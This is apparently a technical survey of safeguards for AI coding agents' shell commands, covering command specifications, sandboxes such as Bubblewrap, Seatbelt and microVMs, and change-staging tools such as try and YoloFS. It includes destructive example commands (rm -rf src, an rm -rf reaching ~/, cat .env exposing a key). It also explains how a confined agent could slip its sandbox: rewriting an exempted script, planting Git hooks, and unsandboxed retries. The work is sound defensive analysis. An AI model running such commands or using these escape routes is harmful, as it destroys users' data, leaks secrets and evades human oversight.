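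When the same command is safe in one situation and unsafe in another, a judge that receives only the text gets the same input in both. If it always gives the same answer, it is wrong in one of them. If it picks "allow" at random with probability q, it is right with probability q when the command is safe and 1 − q when it is not. Its expected number of correct answers over the two situations is q + (1 − q) = 1, the same as for a judge that always blocks the command. A larger model can't improve on this because its input also lacks the information that distinguishes the two situations.

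Taukoor and colleagues tested four models on 15 commands, each paired with a machine state in which it was safe and one in which it was not. A model scored a point only if it judged the command correctly in both states. Given only the command's text, two models scored 0 and the other two scored 1, apparently by luck. Given the rules and the machine's state as well, they scored 13, 11, 4 and 0. The models therefore needed this information to judge the commands correctly, but having it was not always enough.

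The study is small, tested fairly small models, and used rules and cases that were mostly invented for it. The proof does not depend on any of this, but the experiment shows that accuracy figures can be misleading. Across all 50 cases, one model that saw only the text denied everything and was right 66% of the time, while another allowed everything and was right 34% of the time. Their scores differed only because 33 of the cases were unsafe.

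A shell can often supply the missing state easily. It can check whether `2022` is a folder before it sends the command to the judge, and CARE already follows links to find the actual file a path leads to. aegish includes the contents of a script when a command would run one. Determining which facts matter is harder and requires a description of what each command does.

### Specifications: what `rm` needs and what it changes

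A command specification consists of preconditions, which describe the state in which the command starts, and postconditions, which describe what is true when it finishes. For `rm p`, one precondition is that `p` is a file, and the matching postcondition is that the file no longer exists and the exit code is 0. A program returns an exit code of 0 to report success and any other number to report failure.

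Options change the specification, so each combination needs its own entries. This table assumes that the user has permission to delete `p`:

| Command | `p` is a file | `p` is a directory | `p` does not exist |
|---|---|---|---|
| `rm p` | deletes it, exit code 0 | no change, exit code 1 | no change, exit code 1 |
| `rm -r p` | deletes it, exit code 0 | deletes it and its contents, exit code 0 | no change, exit code 1 |
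| `rm -f p` | deletes it, exit code 0 | no change, exit code 1 | no change, exit code 0 |
| `rm -rf p` | deletes it, exit code 0 | deletes it and its contents, exit code 0 | no change, exit code 0 |

`rm -rf` is dangerous in scripts because it reports success in all three states, as the bottom row shows. A script that passes it the wrong path gets no error to stop it.

Specifications become more useful when an analysis chains them, using the postcondition of one command as the starting state of the next. In the photo script, the specification of `mv` needs three cases. If the destination is a folder, the photo moves into it; if it is a file, the photo replaces it; and if it doesn't exist, the photo takes its name. If `2022` doesn't exist at first, moving the first photo from that year makes `2022` a file. Moving the second photo then replaces the first, so the analysis finds the data loss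 without running the script or examining any photos.

Researchers have written such descriptions by hand for years, though often for other purposes. PaSh speeds up shell scripts by running parts of them in parallel, and its annotations record what a command reads and writes and whether it can process its input in pieces. POSH moves work closer to where the data is stored, so its annotations record, for instance, whether a command's output is usually smaller than its input. Gyawali and colleagues want to build on these annotations for NaSh, but a guardrail needs more detail. PaSh's annotations classify `rm` only as a command with side effects, which is enough to rule out running it in parallel but doesn't show which files it will delete.

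### How Caruca derives specifications

Writing specifications by hand takes a lot of time, and every new version of a command may need new ones. *Caruca* (Lamprou, Lazarek and colleagues, 2025) presents a program that derives them automatically in four steps.

1. A language model, GPT-4o, reads the command's documentation and lists its options and arguments along with their types, such as a path or a whole number. If the result isn't valid, the model gets the error message and tries again. The model has no part in the later steps.
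2. Caruca generates many ways to call the command, with up to four options at a time, and pairs each with different file states. A path may lead to a file, an empty directory, a directory with something in it, or nothing at all. For `rm`, this makes 8,749,056 combinations.
3. It runs every combination in a sandbox. A tracing program records the system calls that involve files, and Caruca compares the files before and after the run.
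4. It turns the starting state into the precondition and the observed changes into the postcondition.

A mistake by the language model therefore matters less than it would if the model wrote the specifications itself. If the model overlooks an option, the specification omits that option, but its other entries still come from observing the command as it runs.

Lamprou and colleagues compared Caruca's specifications with handwritten ones for 60 commands and found 59 correct. The exception was `git`, which needs a prepared repository that Caruca can't set up. Some of the handwritten specifications were also wrong. PaSh's annotation for `grep`, for example, doesn't hold when `grep` is counting matching lines. In a test of the first step on 120 commands, the model got every option and argument right for 116. With at most two options per call, Caruca finished 103 of the 120 commands within an hour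 each.

To check how well this covers everyday use, Lamprou and colleagues collected about 666,000 command calls from scripts on GitHub. Caruca had tested the equivalent of 98% of them, but only about 10% matched exactly. Most of the other matches depend on the assumption that a command behaves the same way whatever text it receives as an argument. That is reasonable for a command that prints text but, as the researchers point out, not for `xargs`, which runs other commands named in its arguments. When they limited the assumption to commands that use the text for printing or filtering, about 35% of the calls matched, before they also allowed for different numbers of arguments.

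Caruca doesn't model symbolic links or vary the settings that programs inherit from the shell. The first omission matters for guardrails because a specification that covers only files and directories can't describe folders that point somewhere else. Such folders in a test environment led to the deletion of 48,218 live files.

### From specifications to warnings

ShellCheck and Shseer look for bugs in shell scripts without running them. ShellCheck, which is widely used, recognizes common mistakes from the way a script is written. Many of its 47 checks for particular commands concern style, quotation marks or commands built into the shell, but six depend on the kind of facts that Caruca, the system by Lamprou and colleagues, can derive. For example, if a command is known to delete its arguments, ShellCheck can warn when a script passes it a system directory. ShellCheck gave the same results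 on its own tests with the derived versions of these six checks as with the handwritten ones. Caruca's results also suggested new checks, including one for `rmdir`, which removes empty directories.

Shseer tracks the state of the filesystem through the script, allowing for unknown arguments and files. It uses each command's preconditions and postconditions to work out what the command could do to them. It mainly looks for scripts that might accidentally delete a system directory, such as the one-line `delete.sh`, where the path before `/*` can be empty. In a test with 12 buggy scripts written by Shseer's developers, it found all 12 bugs using Caruca's specifications. That is encouraging, but every script had a bug, so the test doesn't show how often Shseer would raise a false alarm on good code.

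These tools also need to know exactly which arguments the shell will pass to each command. This is hard because the shell first rewrites the text through word expansion, which replaces variables with their values, splits the result at spaces, and turns patterns such as `*.log` into lists of filenames. If the variable `x` contains `a b`, then `rm $x` deletes two files, `a` and `b`, while `rm "$x"` deletes one file named `a b`. *Executable formal semantics for the POSIX shell* (Greenberg and Blatt, 2019) mentions a script from the game platform Steam that wiped users' hard drives because it got word expansion wrong.

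Greenberg and Blatt wrote a formal semantics for the shell language, a mathematical definition of what every construct does. Their definition, Smoosh, also runs as a shell, so they could test it against seven existing shells. It followed POSIX, the standard for Unix shells, more closely than any of them, and the work uncovered bugs in several of them and in the standard. Smoosh can also simulate system calls, so a user can watch a command expand step by step without changing any real files.

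Researchers need a definition of the shell language, such as Smoosh, to prove things about an analysis tool. They could then prove, for example, that whenever the tool reports that a script never deletes anything outside a certain directory, the report is true of every possible run. The proof would still depend on accurate specifications of commands such as `rm` and `cp`, which Smoosh does not define. It would also depend on which shell the user has, because the shell standard leaves many details open and real shells may interpret them differently from Smoosh.

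### What a check can establish

A check can calculate a command's effect before the command runs if the specification, the arguments and the state of the files are all known. For `rm /logs/*.log` and the five example files, the shell could expand the pattern and tell the user that the command will delete only `app.log`. A beginner could understand that and see that the hidden log file would remain. A summary measured after the run would need no specification, but it would come too late to prevent a leak.

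Calculating a command's effect does not show whether the user wanted it. The request to delete all log files has eight reasonable readings, and a check can only determine what one command would do. A judge that also receives the request can compare it with the command's effect, but the request is as ambiguous to the judge as it was to the model that wrote the command.

A check can also be out of date by the time the command runs. For example, another program may replace a folder with a file after the shell checks it but before `mv` runs. Checks on single commands also miss harmful plans spread over several commands, as Liu and colleagues acknowledge for CARE. One command may download a file, the next make it executable, and a third run it, with each step looking ordinary on its own.

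Imperfect checks can still reduce the risk considerably. In the earlier example of a 300-command session, a guard that stopped 76% of the damaging commands would lower the chance of an accident from 26% to about 7%. But that assumes CARE would catch an agent's accidents as reliably as it catches the attacks in its test set, and nobody has shown this.

Commands that run other people's code are the hardest to check. A correct specification of `cargo build` would have to cover compiling the project and anything the project's build scripts might do. The shell could read those scripts first, but they may start further programs, and a large project can have hundreds of dependencies. Asking the user about each build wouldn't help much either, since the user has no more information about the scripts than the shell does.

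## Limiting what a running command can reach

A shell can keep `cargo build` away from the user's keys without predicting what it will do. Confinement works because every program opens files and network connections through the operating system, which can refuse a request no matter which script made it. A harness can't do this because, as NVIDIA points out in security advice on coding agents, it has no control over the programs that a command starts.

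### From user accounts to virtual machines

The oldest limit of this kind is the user account. Each file has an owner and a list of who may read or change it, and the kernel, the core of the operating system, checks that list whenever a program opens the file. These permissions protect system files and other people's documents, but not the user's own files, because the agent runs under the user's account. @IT, a Japanese technology site, retells a case from December 2025 in which a developer asked Claude Code to tidy an old repository. The agent ran an `rm -rf` that seemed to list three project directories but ended in `~/`, the home directory. The developer owned everything in it, so the permissions allowed the deletion. The deleted files included the keychain, where macOS stores passwords.

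Linux kernel namespaces can also give a command a restricted view of the computer. A mount namespace gives the command a private directory tree, and the command can't open a file missing from that tree, even given its path. Other namespaces hide running programs or cut the command off from the network. Bubblewrap is a small tool that builds such a view around a single command. A harness could use it to make the project writable and the system's programs read-only, and leave out the home directory. As Zhong and colleagues point out, Bubblewrap builds the view at launch, so a harness has to start a new sandbox to expose another directory.

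Landlock, another part of the Linux kernel, restricts access without changing the directory tree. A program gives the kernel a list of directories and what it may do in each, and the kernel enforces the list on the program and everything it starts. The program can add restrictions later but never remove them, so malicious code can't lift them and the harness can't grant a running command an exception. Some harnesses add seccomp, which blocks whole types of system call.

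macOS has a built-in sandbox called Seatbelt. The harness writes a profile of permitted operations and starts the command under that profile. Chrome and Apple's own applications also use Seatbelt, according to Cursor's *Agent Sandboxing*. Windows has no ready-made tool for sandboxing a coding agent, so OpenAI built its own sandbox for Codex.

A container combines namespaces with a separate set of system files. The command sees the container's own programs and any of the user's directories attached to it. The command still uses the host's kernel, so a kernel flaw could let it escape. gVisor reduces that risk by intercepting the container's system calls and handling them in a second kernel, written in Go, according to Google's *Sandboxing in Gemini CLI*. Anthropic uses gVisor for its web application Claude.ai, according to Willison's (2026) summary of the company's own account.

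A small virtual machine, or microVM, isolates a command further by running its own kernel on simulated hardware. Docker Sandboxes puts each agent in one. The user's home directory doesn't exist inside it, and by default Docker blocks attaching directories that hold keys, such as `~/.ssh` and `~/.aws`. The `rm -rf` from December 2025 would have deleted the contents of the attached project there, but not the keychain.

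| Mechanism | Blocks | Leaves open | Main cost | Can the rules change during a run? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| User permissions | System files, other users' files | Everything the user owns | None | Yes |
| Namespaces, through Bubblewrap | Files, programs and networks outside the view | Attached directories; the shared kernel | Some Linux systems block it until an administrator adds an exception | No, only in a new sandbox |
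| Landlock | File operations that are not on the list | Listed directories; many effects other than file access | Linux only, and older kernels cover less | Only to make them stricter |
| Seatbelt | Operations that the profile forbids | Whatever the profile permits | macOS only; some tools fail under it | No, but the next command can get a new profile |
| Container | Host files that nobody attached | Attached directories; the shared kernel | Someone has to install every tool inside | No, only in a new container |
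| MicroVM | The same, and most attacks on the host's kernel | Attached directories; any secrets inside | More memory, a slower start, and tools to install | Usually not for attached directories |

Anthropic explains that limits on file and network access depend on each other. An agent with unrestricted network access could send out any key it can read, and an agent that can write anywhere could change the system to regain network access.

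### What the products confine by default

Makers change their defaults often, so each entry in the table is dated. The details for Cursor, Gemini CLI and Copilot come mainly from Zhong and colleagues' comparison, and the rest come from the makers' documentation.

| Product | Confines shell commands by default? | Mechanism | As of |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | No | Seatbelt on macOS, Bubblewrap on Linux | October 2026 |
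| Codex CLI | Yes | Seatbelt, Bubblewrap with seccomp, its own sandbox on Windows | June 2026 |
| Cursor | Yes | Seatbelt, Landlock | Spring 2026 |
| Gemini CLI | No | Docker; gVisor is an option | Spring 2026 |
| VS Code Copilot | No | Bubblewrap | Spring 2026 |
| Docker Sandboxes | Yes, the sandbox is the product | MicroVM | June 2026 |

When a user turns on Claude Code's sandbox, it applies to shell commands and the programs they start. According to Anthropic's sandboxing guide, these can write only to the project, a temporary directory and any directories the user has added. They can still read nearly the whole disk, including files with passwords and keys, unless the user blocks those paths. On Windows, the sandbox works only inside WSL2, Microsoft's system for running Linux within Windows.

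Other parts of Claude Code run outside the sandbox boundary. Its built-in file tools follow separate permission rules, so blocking a file in the sandbox settings doesn't stop the Read tool from opening it. Hooks (scripts that the harness runs at set moments) and local MCP servers (which connect the agent to other software) have the user's full access. If these parts need a boundary too, Anthropic recommends running all of Claude Code inside a container or similar wrapper.

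Users can also exempt commands by name, and they need to do this for `docker`, which doesn't work in the sandbox. A chain of commands runs outside the sandbox only if every command in it is exempt, so `npm ci && docker compose build` stays confined unless the user has exempted `npm ci` as well. An exempt command has the user's full access. Anthropic warns that if an exemption covers a script in the project, Claude can rewrite the script and then run it outside the sandbox.

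When a command fails inside the sandbox, Claude may retry it outside. In the ordinary mode, the user gets a prompt that labels the command as unsandboxed. But an allow rule for the command also covers the retry, so a user who allowed `make *` to avoid interruptions has also allowed it to run outside the sandbox without a prompt. A strict mode turns these retries off. If the sandbox can't start, for example because Bubblewrap is missing, Claude Code runs commands without it unless the user has set it to quit instead.

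By default, commands that Codex runs can write only to the current directory and temporary directories, and have no network access, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* (June 2026). OpenAI's Chinese-language permissions page, *权限*, still gave that default in September. When a command needs more access, Codex asks the user, who can have a reviewing model handle such requests. Users can also write rules that let commands starting with given words run outside the sandbox, according to OpenAI's *Sandbox*. Zhong and colleagues, who tested version 0.101, list Landlock as the sandboxing mechanism on Linux, but OpenAI switched to Bubblewrap in version 0.115.

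Cursor also runs sandboxed commands without a prompt, and its agent asks for approval when it has to leave the sandbox. Users can instead require approval for every action. Docker starts agents without approval prompts because it relies on the virtual machine for safety. For Gemini, Docker also switches off the agent's own sandbox.

A confined command can do harm later by writing a file that something outside the sandbox will run. One example is a Git hook, a script that Git runs automatically at certain points, such as before a commit, which the user may make outside the sandbox. Zed, a code editor that confines its agent by default, forbids writing to the `.git` directory for this reason. Codex also makes the whole of `.git` read-only, so an agent has to leave the sandbox to commit its work. Claude Code protects shell startup files and its own configuration, but within `.git` it protects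 only the hooks and settings. Agents can therefore commit without leaving the sandbox, though a mistaken deletion could erase the project's history.

Virtual machines have the same weakness. An agent in a Docker sandbox shares the project directory with the host and can leave a script there for the user to run, although Docker claims that its sandboxes leave "no path back to the host".

### How many prompts confinement saves

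Cursor reports that sandboxed agents stop 40% less often than unsandboxed ones and that most of the remaining requests are for internet access. Cursor measured its own product, and the figure covers interruptions rather than accidents.

Zhong and colleagues counted the permission prompts that several products showed on 112 small tasks, each a single operation such as copying or deleting a file. Some paths were inside the project, some were outside, and some led outside through a symbolic link. Their test program accepted every request and chose "don't ask again" whenever it could. The table gives the average number of prompts per task.

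| Harness | Inside the project | Outside | Through a link | All tasks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex | 0 | 0.8 | 0.6 | 0.4 |
| Claude Code | 0.8 | 1.1 | 1.0 | 0.9 |
| Copilot | 0.7 | 1.8 | 1.7 | 1.3 |
| Gemini CLI | 1.3 | 2.3 | 4.2 | 2.2 |

Codex was the only one of the four with a sandbox on by default, and it never asked about work inside the project. But the products differ in other ways, so these numbers don't isolate the effect of confinement. Gemini, for example, kept retrying after its rules had refused access to an outside path. Codex asked rarely but did more work, averaging 1.8 tool calls per task, because it tried commands inside the sandbox and had to rerun some outside.

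### Too tight and too loose at once

Suppose a developer keeps the code for an online shop in `~/shop`. There, `src` contains a day's uncommitted work, and `.env` holds the key to the payment service. The tests need a database that runs on the same Linux laptop. The harness lets commands write only to `~/shop` and connect only to the site that supplies software packages.

| Command | Result in the sandbox | What the developer wants |
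|---|---|---|
| `npm install` | Fails when it has to write to a package cache in the home directory | Success |
| `npm test` | Fails because it can't reach the database | Success |
| `cat .env` | Prints the payment key | A refusal or a question |
| `rm -rf src` | Deletes the day's work | A refusal or a question |

The boundary would still protect the photos in the developer's home directory, but it gives the wrong result for all four of these commands. Zhong and colleagues collected reports of sandboxes blocking legitimate work, including test suites, builds and access to graphics processors.

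The developer can get the first two commands to work. `npm install` can run inside the sandbox once the package cache is added to the writable directories. The tests are harder because, in Claude Code's sandbox on Linux, a command can't connect directly to a server running outside the sandbox on the same machine. Anthropic advises running commands that need such a connection unconfined, which gives the tests the user's full access even though the agent writes and edits them.

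A wider boundary causes fewer failures but exposes more files. OpenAI says in an account of its internal use of Codex that it makes the sandbox compulsory and adds `~/development` to the writable area. Developers who keep their projects there can let the agent move between them without an approval prompt, but a mistake in one project can then damage the others.

Asking the user to approve running a failed command outside the sandbox doesn't solve the problem either. Zhong and colleagues gave Codex 11 tasks in which a routine command, such as a code formatter, also deleted or overwrote files it should have left alone. Codex tried each command in its sandbox, hit a restriction, and asked whether to run it outside. The prompt showed the command but not its hidden effects, so a user who wanted the code formatted had little reason to refuse. In the reports, repeated requests like these led people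 to turn the sandbox off altogether.

### Asking when the command reaches the file

An ordinary sandbox has to allow or refuse each access immediately, using rules written in advance. YoloFS can also pause the command and ask the user about the file, an approach Zhong and colleagues call progressive permission.

Each rule in YoloFS assigns one of five policies to a path:

| Policy | Reading the file or running it | Changing it |
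|---|---|---|
| `allow` | Permitted | Permitted |
| `read-only` | Permitted | Refused |
| `write-ask` | Permitted | YoloFS asks |
| `ask` | YoloFS asks | YoloFS asks |
| `deny` | Refused | Refused |

A path without its own rule takes the policy of the nearest directory above it that has one. The developer of the online shop could set `allow` for `~/shop` and `ask` for both `~/shop/.env` and the rest of the home directory.

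The `cargo build` with the malicious dependency shows how this works:

1. The harness passes the command to YoloFS's command-line program, which starts it with YoloFS as its entire filesystem. The build and every script it launches can reach files only through YoloFS.
2. The compiler reads and writes in the project. The policy there is `allow`, so YoloFS doesn't interrupt it.
3. The malicious script tries to read the user's private key, `~/.ssh/id_rsa`. The file has no rule of its own, so the `ask` policy on the home directory applies.
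4. YoloFS pauses the thread that made the request, and the user sees the path, the operation and the name of the program.
5. The user denies the request and chooses not to see it again. YoloFS refuses the access and saves a `deny` rule for that path. If the user had not answered in time, YoloFS would also have refused.
6. After the command ends, YoloFS shows the agent which access it blocked. The agent can then recognize the attack and try another dependency.

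New rules take effect at the next access, even while a command is running, and YoloFS saves them for later sessions in the same project. The agent can't approve its own requests or edit the rules, because the kernel part of YoloFS rejects such calls from programs running inside YoloFS. The project can stay accessible to the agent because YoloFS doesn't apply the agent's file changes until the user accepts them.

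It is much easier to decide whether to allow access to `~/.ssh/id_rsa` than whether to allow `cargo build`, since a compiler has no need for that SSH key. The decision also applies to any other program the agent might try instead.

On the 112 small tasks, Claude Code needed 0.4 answers from the user per task with YoloFS and 0.9 without it. It completed 99% of the tasks with YoloFS and 98% without. The permission checks slowed most file operations negligibly, but they slowed the call that looks up a file's details by 4%.

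These results may not hold for larger jobs. Each task was a single operation, while a real build may access dozens of locations outside the project. The test program also approved every request, so the experiment shows how often YoloFS prompts for approval but not how well people would judge those prompts.

A path alone doesn't always show whether access is legitimate. `git push` may need the same SSH key that a malicious build script tries to read. If the user permanently allows access to the key, the rule applies to every program, and the next malicious build script can read it without a prompt. The user could instead approve each push separately, but that means more prompts. YoloFS also runs only on Linux and controls only files, so network access needs a separate limit.

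Other products implement parts of this idea. Claude Code can hold a confined command while the user decides whether to allow a new network address, but it doesn't do this for files. In Zed, the agent can request extra privileges for a limited time and has to give a reason. That request is based on a need described in the model's output, whereas YoloFS reports an access that a program attempted.

### Choosing a boundary

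Soldani (2026), in *Claude Code Complete User Handbook*, classes written instructions to an agent as advice, in contrast to permission rules, sandboxes and isolation by the operating system, which software enforces. To choose an enforced boundary, a user can go through these steps:

1. List the directories the task has to change, the files it has to read and the network addresses it has to contact.
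2. Choose the mechanism according to whose code will run. For a familiar project and an agent that may make mistakes, Bubblewrap or Seatbelt around each command is a reasonable start. For unfamiliar code or unattended work, use a microVM that contains only the keys the task needs.
3. Find out which parts of the harness remain outside, such as hooks and MCP servers. If they could do harm, confine the whole harness.
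4. Block access to password files and keys explicitly, because a sandbox that limits writing may still let commands read them.
5. When a legitimate command fails, add the one directory or address it needs. Exempt the whole program only if that doesn't work, and never exempt a script that the agent can edit.
6. For unattended work, turn off unconfined retries and set the harness to quit if the sandbox can't start.
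7. Test the boundary before relying on it, since misconfigured boundaries failed in practice in 2026. Have the agent try to create a file in the home directory and read a dummy key. In Claude Code, a command that the user types usually runs outside the sandbox, so it has to be the agent that tries.
8. Keep a copy of the project where the agent can't write, because a boundary around the project doesn't protect the files inside it.

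## Holding back or undoing changes to files

An agent has to change the project's files to do its job, but a shell can still let the user reject the changes. The shell can stage the changes until the user accepts them, or it can change the real files at once and keep the old versions so the user can undo the edits. In both designs, the user eventually commits the changes, which makes them final, or aborts them, which discards them.

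### Two layers that look like one directory

Staging tools often use an overlay filesystem. Linux includes one called OverlayFS, which shows two directory trees as if they were one. The lower layer holds the original files, and OverlayFS never writes to it. The upper layer starts empty and receives every change. When a program opens a file, OverlayFS checks the upper layer first and then the lower one.

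If a program opens a file from the lower layer for writing, OverlayFS first copies the whole file to the upper layer, and the program changes the copy (copy on first write). When a program deletes a file, OverlayFS can't remove it from the lower layer, so it puts a whiteout in the upper layer, a marker that hides the file of the same name below.

Suppose a model answers the request to delete the log files in `/logs` with a script that runs `find /logs -name '*.log' -delete` and then adds a line to `README`. With an overlay on top of `/logs`, the five example files look like this afterward:

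| File | Lower layer | Upper layer | What the script sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| `app.log` | original | whiteout | no file |
| `app.log.1` | original | nothing | original |
| `.system.log` | original | whiteout | no file |
| `web/access.log` | original | whiteout | no file |
| `README` | original | copy with the new line | the new version |

Programs outside the overlay still see the five original files. A tool can abort the changes just by discarding the upper layer. It commits them by deleting the three log files from the real directory and replacing `README`.

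### Running a command under `try`

The Linux tool `try` does this for any command the user types after its name, and it doesn't need administrator rights. Lamprou and colleagues describe three stages:

1. `try` creates an upper layer and puts a separate overlay on each top-level directory, such as `/home` and `/etc`. A single overlay for the whole system wouldn't work, because the upper layer would then lie inside the lower one, and OverlayFS forbids that.
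2. It starts the command in new namespaces, where these overlays take the place of the real directories. Any programs that the command starts get the same view.
3. When the command ends, `try` lists the files it added, changed or deleted and asks whether to apply the changes. If the user agrees, `try` moves the new files to their real places and deletes the files that the whiteouts cover.

For the faulty `delete.sh` that could delete everything the user owns, the list begins with `/home` and `/etc`, and the user can refuse.

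The user can also accept only some of the changes. A colleague of the developers ran a machine-learning job under `try` and kept only the best of the models it had saved. A partial commit can leave files inconsistent, for example if the user accepts a new file but refuses the directory it belongs in. `try` warns about that case, but it can't detect when a new settings file only works with a program update the user has refused.

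`try` can save a set of changes under a name and run the next command on top of them. That command then works with the earlier changes, even though the real files are still untouched. The developers' students have also run whole agent sessions under `try` and inspected the changes at the end.

Lamprou and colleagues ran 25 tasks with and without `try` and compared checksums of the entire filesystem after each run. The final state was the same once `try` had applied the changes. The slowdown depended mainly on how long the command itself took.

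| Type of task | Slowdown compared with running it directly | Speedup compared with Docker |
|---|---|---|
| Scripts written by ChatGPT | 1.1 to 1.9 times | 1.3 to 225.7 times |
| Scripts whose commands depend on each other | 1.0 to 1.7 times | 1.1 to 18.7 times |
| Risky Git hooks | 1.0 to 1.3 times | 1.4 to 4.2 times |
| Recording which files a command reads and writes | 1.7 to 8.3 times | 1.6 to 2.2 times |
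| Replacing a command's own dry-run mode | 4.9 to 82.6 times | 1.2 to 3.2 times |

The paper gives the slowdown as 1.0 to 8.3 times, which leaves out the last row. A dry-run mode reports what a command would do without doing it, so it finishes quickly. The five dry runs took 0.03 seconds on average, and the same commands under `try` took 0.26 seconds. Few users would notice the difference in a single command.

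Most of this overhead is fixed. A program that did nothing took 165 milliseconds under `try`, mainly to set up and remove the overlays and namespaces. At that rate, a session of 300 commands would take about 50 seconds longer, which is little compared with the time the model needs to write them. Creating 10,000 small files took 11 seconds, including 6.3 seconds to close the namespace.

The comparison with Docker overstates the speed advantage of `try`. In these tests, Docker had to copy the input files into a new container and the results back out, which explains the largest speedups. A harness that attaches the project directory to a container doesn't need these copies, but users can't review the changes before they're made.

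### Why `try` is only a "semisolate"

Lamprou and colleagues call the environment that `try` creates a "semisolate". Unlike a container, which gives a command a new environment, `try` lets the command see the user's existing one, including all the installed programs, settings and documents. This gives an installer everything it needs, but it also lets hostile code read the user's keys.

By default, the command can also use the network. If the user ran `cargo build` under `try`, the malicious dependency could read the SSH key and send it to an attacker. Sending the key changes no files, so it wouldn't appear in the list at the end. The project's README, *Do, or do not. There is no try*, describes the tool as a prototype and "not a full sandbox", and warns users against running commands they don't already trust.

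The user can make the semisolate stricter by turning off the network or hiding chosen files from the command. In the tests with Git hooks, the attack tried to copy the system's list of user accounts into a project's `README`, and `try` prevented this because the researchers had hidden that list. Users can only hide a file if they know in advance that it needs protection.

Some of the paper's examples are riskier than the README's warning advises. One runs an installer straight from the internet, and another tests the JavaScript library `node-ipc`, whose earlier versions changed critical system files. `try` helps against hostile code that only damages files and wasn't written with an overlay in mind, but the user can't tell beforehand whether that is all the code will do.

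Some harmless programs also behave differently under `try`. The command appears to run as the administrator inside its namespace, so it can write to files that the user has marked read-only. `npm` may act differently for the same reason. The command can't send signals to programs outside the namespace.

### Changing the real files and keeping the old ones

Gyawali and colleagues wanted NaSh to let users delay the decision for as long as possible, because mistakes in generated commands may surface late. They give three reasons why ordinary overlays don't suit this:

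- Other programs can't see the changes until the user commits them, and after that the user can no longer undo them.
- If each command gets its own overlay, the layers pile up. To find a file, the system may have to search them one after another.
- Changes to special files in `/proc` and `/sys`, which Linux uses for system settings, don't take effect in an overlay.

NaSh would use an inverse overlay instead. Each command changes the real files directly, and a separate layer keeps the old versions. If the script from the earlier example ran this way, the three log files would disappear from `/logs` immediately and `README` would have its new line. The layer would hold the three deleted files and the old `README`. NaSh would put them back to abort the script, or discard them to commit its changes.

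These layers don't slow down later commands, because programs read the real files directly. The main limit is disk space. Gyawali and colleagues compare committing to emptying a recycle bin and suggest that the shell could commit the oldest commands automatically when the disk fills up. A single command could still exhaust the space. If a script overwrites 200 GB of video on a disk with 100 GB free, the shell has to stop it or lose the ability to undo some of its changes.

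The first of the three arguments is the most convincing. Someone who has asked a shell to sort photos will want to open them in an ordinary photo viewer before deciding whether the result is right. But if other programs can read the changes immediately, they can also act on the mistakes. If the shell wrongly deletes photos, a synchronization program may delete them from the user's phone too, and a web server may start serving a broken page. Restoring the old files doesn't undo what those programs did in the meantime.

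The argument about special files has a similar weakness. An inverse overlay could restore a changed setting by writing the old value back, but writing to some special files triggers actions. For example, an administrator can restart the computer immediately by writing to a file in `/proc`, and restoring that file's old contents would not undo the restart.

NaSh exists only as a design, so the speed of an inverse overlay is unknown. The design would also have to keep the old versions of files where the agent can't delete them.

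### Undoing one command out of several

NaSh would let the user undo a command while keeping the effects of later ones, or restore only some of the files the command changed. This is useful when the user has done more work since the mistake. It can also cause conflicts, because later commands may have relied on the changes being undone.

Suppose that command X changes the port number in a settings file and command Y later changes the color scheme in the same file. The original is version 1, X produces version 2, and Y produces version 3. Undoing X by restoring version 1 would also remove the new color scheme. Gyawali and colleagues propose storing a version number for each file in both the real filesystem and the inverse overlay. The shell could then detect that the file had changed since X and ask the user what to do.

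This check only works when both commands changed the same file. In an example from Gyawali and colleagues, command X installs a software package and command Y installs a second package that needs the first. Undoing only X breaks the second package.

Whether version numbers would reveal this problem depends on how the package manager stores its records. Python's `pip` gives each package its own directory and record, so X and Y could change no files in common. The check would then find no conflict, and the user would discover the problem when the second package failed to start.

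Debian's package manager keeps its list of installed packages in one file, which both X and Y change. The check would find a conflict there, but either answer would leave the list wrong. The old list omits the second package, whose files would still be on the disk, and the new list includes the first package, whose files would be gone. The user would have to uninstall both packages with the package manager or undo Y before X.

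Gyawali and colleagues note that to detect such conflicts, the shell would have to trace every file that commands read and get hints from the applications. `try` already has an option that records reads and writes in order. In tests by Lamprou and colleagues, this option identified all the true dependencies between commands in five sets of scripts. But a record of the installation may not be enough, because the second package may read the first one's files only when it runs, perhaps weeks later. Commands also read many files that everything else on the system uses, so warning about every shared file would produce mostly false alarms.

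Staged changes can also conflict with the user's edits. If the user edits a file while an agent's version of it is waiting for approval, a commit that replaces the real file will erase the user's edit.

### How YoloFS avoids the costs of layers

YoloFS also stages changes, but without a stack of layers. Zhong and colleagues identified two problems with using OverlayFS for coding agents. Renaming a file copies its entire contents to the upper layer, even though they haven't changed. A single upper layer also holds only the combined result of all the commands, so undoing a single command requires giving each command its own layer.

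YoloFS separates a file's contents from its path, using three data structures:

- The flat file store is a directory that holds the contents of new and changed files under plain numbers.
- The override tree, which the kernel keeps in memory, records where the contents of each changed path are. A path can point to a file in the store, to a file in the real filesystem, or to nothing if a command has deleted it.
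- The session journal is a file on the disk that lists every change to the override tree in order.

Suppose a directory contains the video `film.mov` and the text file `notes.txt`. The table shows what each path points to as an agent works.

| Step | Journal entry | `film.mov` | `wedding.mov` | `notes.txt` |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Start | none | real `film.mov` | nothing | real `notes.txt` |
| 1. A command renames the video | rename | nothing | real `film.mov` | real `notes.txt` |
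| 2. A command adds a line to the notes | stage | nothing | real `film.mov` | stored file 1 |
| 3. A command deletes the notes | delete | nothing | real `film.mov` | nothing |
| 4. The agent goes back to the state after step 2 | travel | nothing | real `film.mov` | stored file 1 |

The rename in step 1 copies nothing because `wedding.mov` points to the old file. If the user commits the session after step 4, YoloFS renames the real video and replaces the real notes with stored file 1. If the user aborts it, YoloFS clears the tree, the store and the journal.

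By default, YoloFS takes a snapshot after every command by adding a marker to the journal, so the snapshot itself copies no files. If a later command opens `notes.txt` for writing again, YoloFS creates a new stored file and keeps the old one in case the agent wants to return to it.

When the agent goes back to a snapshot, YoloFS finds the journal entries that led to that state, replays them and installs the resulting tree. It keeps the entries it skipped, so the agent can return to an abandoned state if going back was a mistake, and the user can still see what the agent tried. The journal also lets YoloFS rebuild the current state after a crash.

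YoloFS needs to read only the entries between two markers to work out what one command changed, because each entry also records what the path pointed to before.

Zhong and colleagues measured the speed of YoloFS on one computer with a solid-state drive. YoloFS stayed within 2% of the speed of ext4, a standard Linux filesystem, when reading and writing a staged 1 GB file, while OverlayFS was up to 23% slower. As the number of snapshots grew, OverlayFS took longer to create new files and to read unchanged ones, but YoloFS did not slow down. OverlayFS failed after about 50 snapshots because the list of layers became too long for the kernel to accept.

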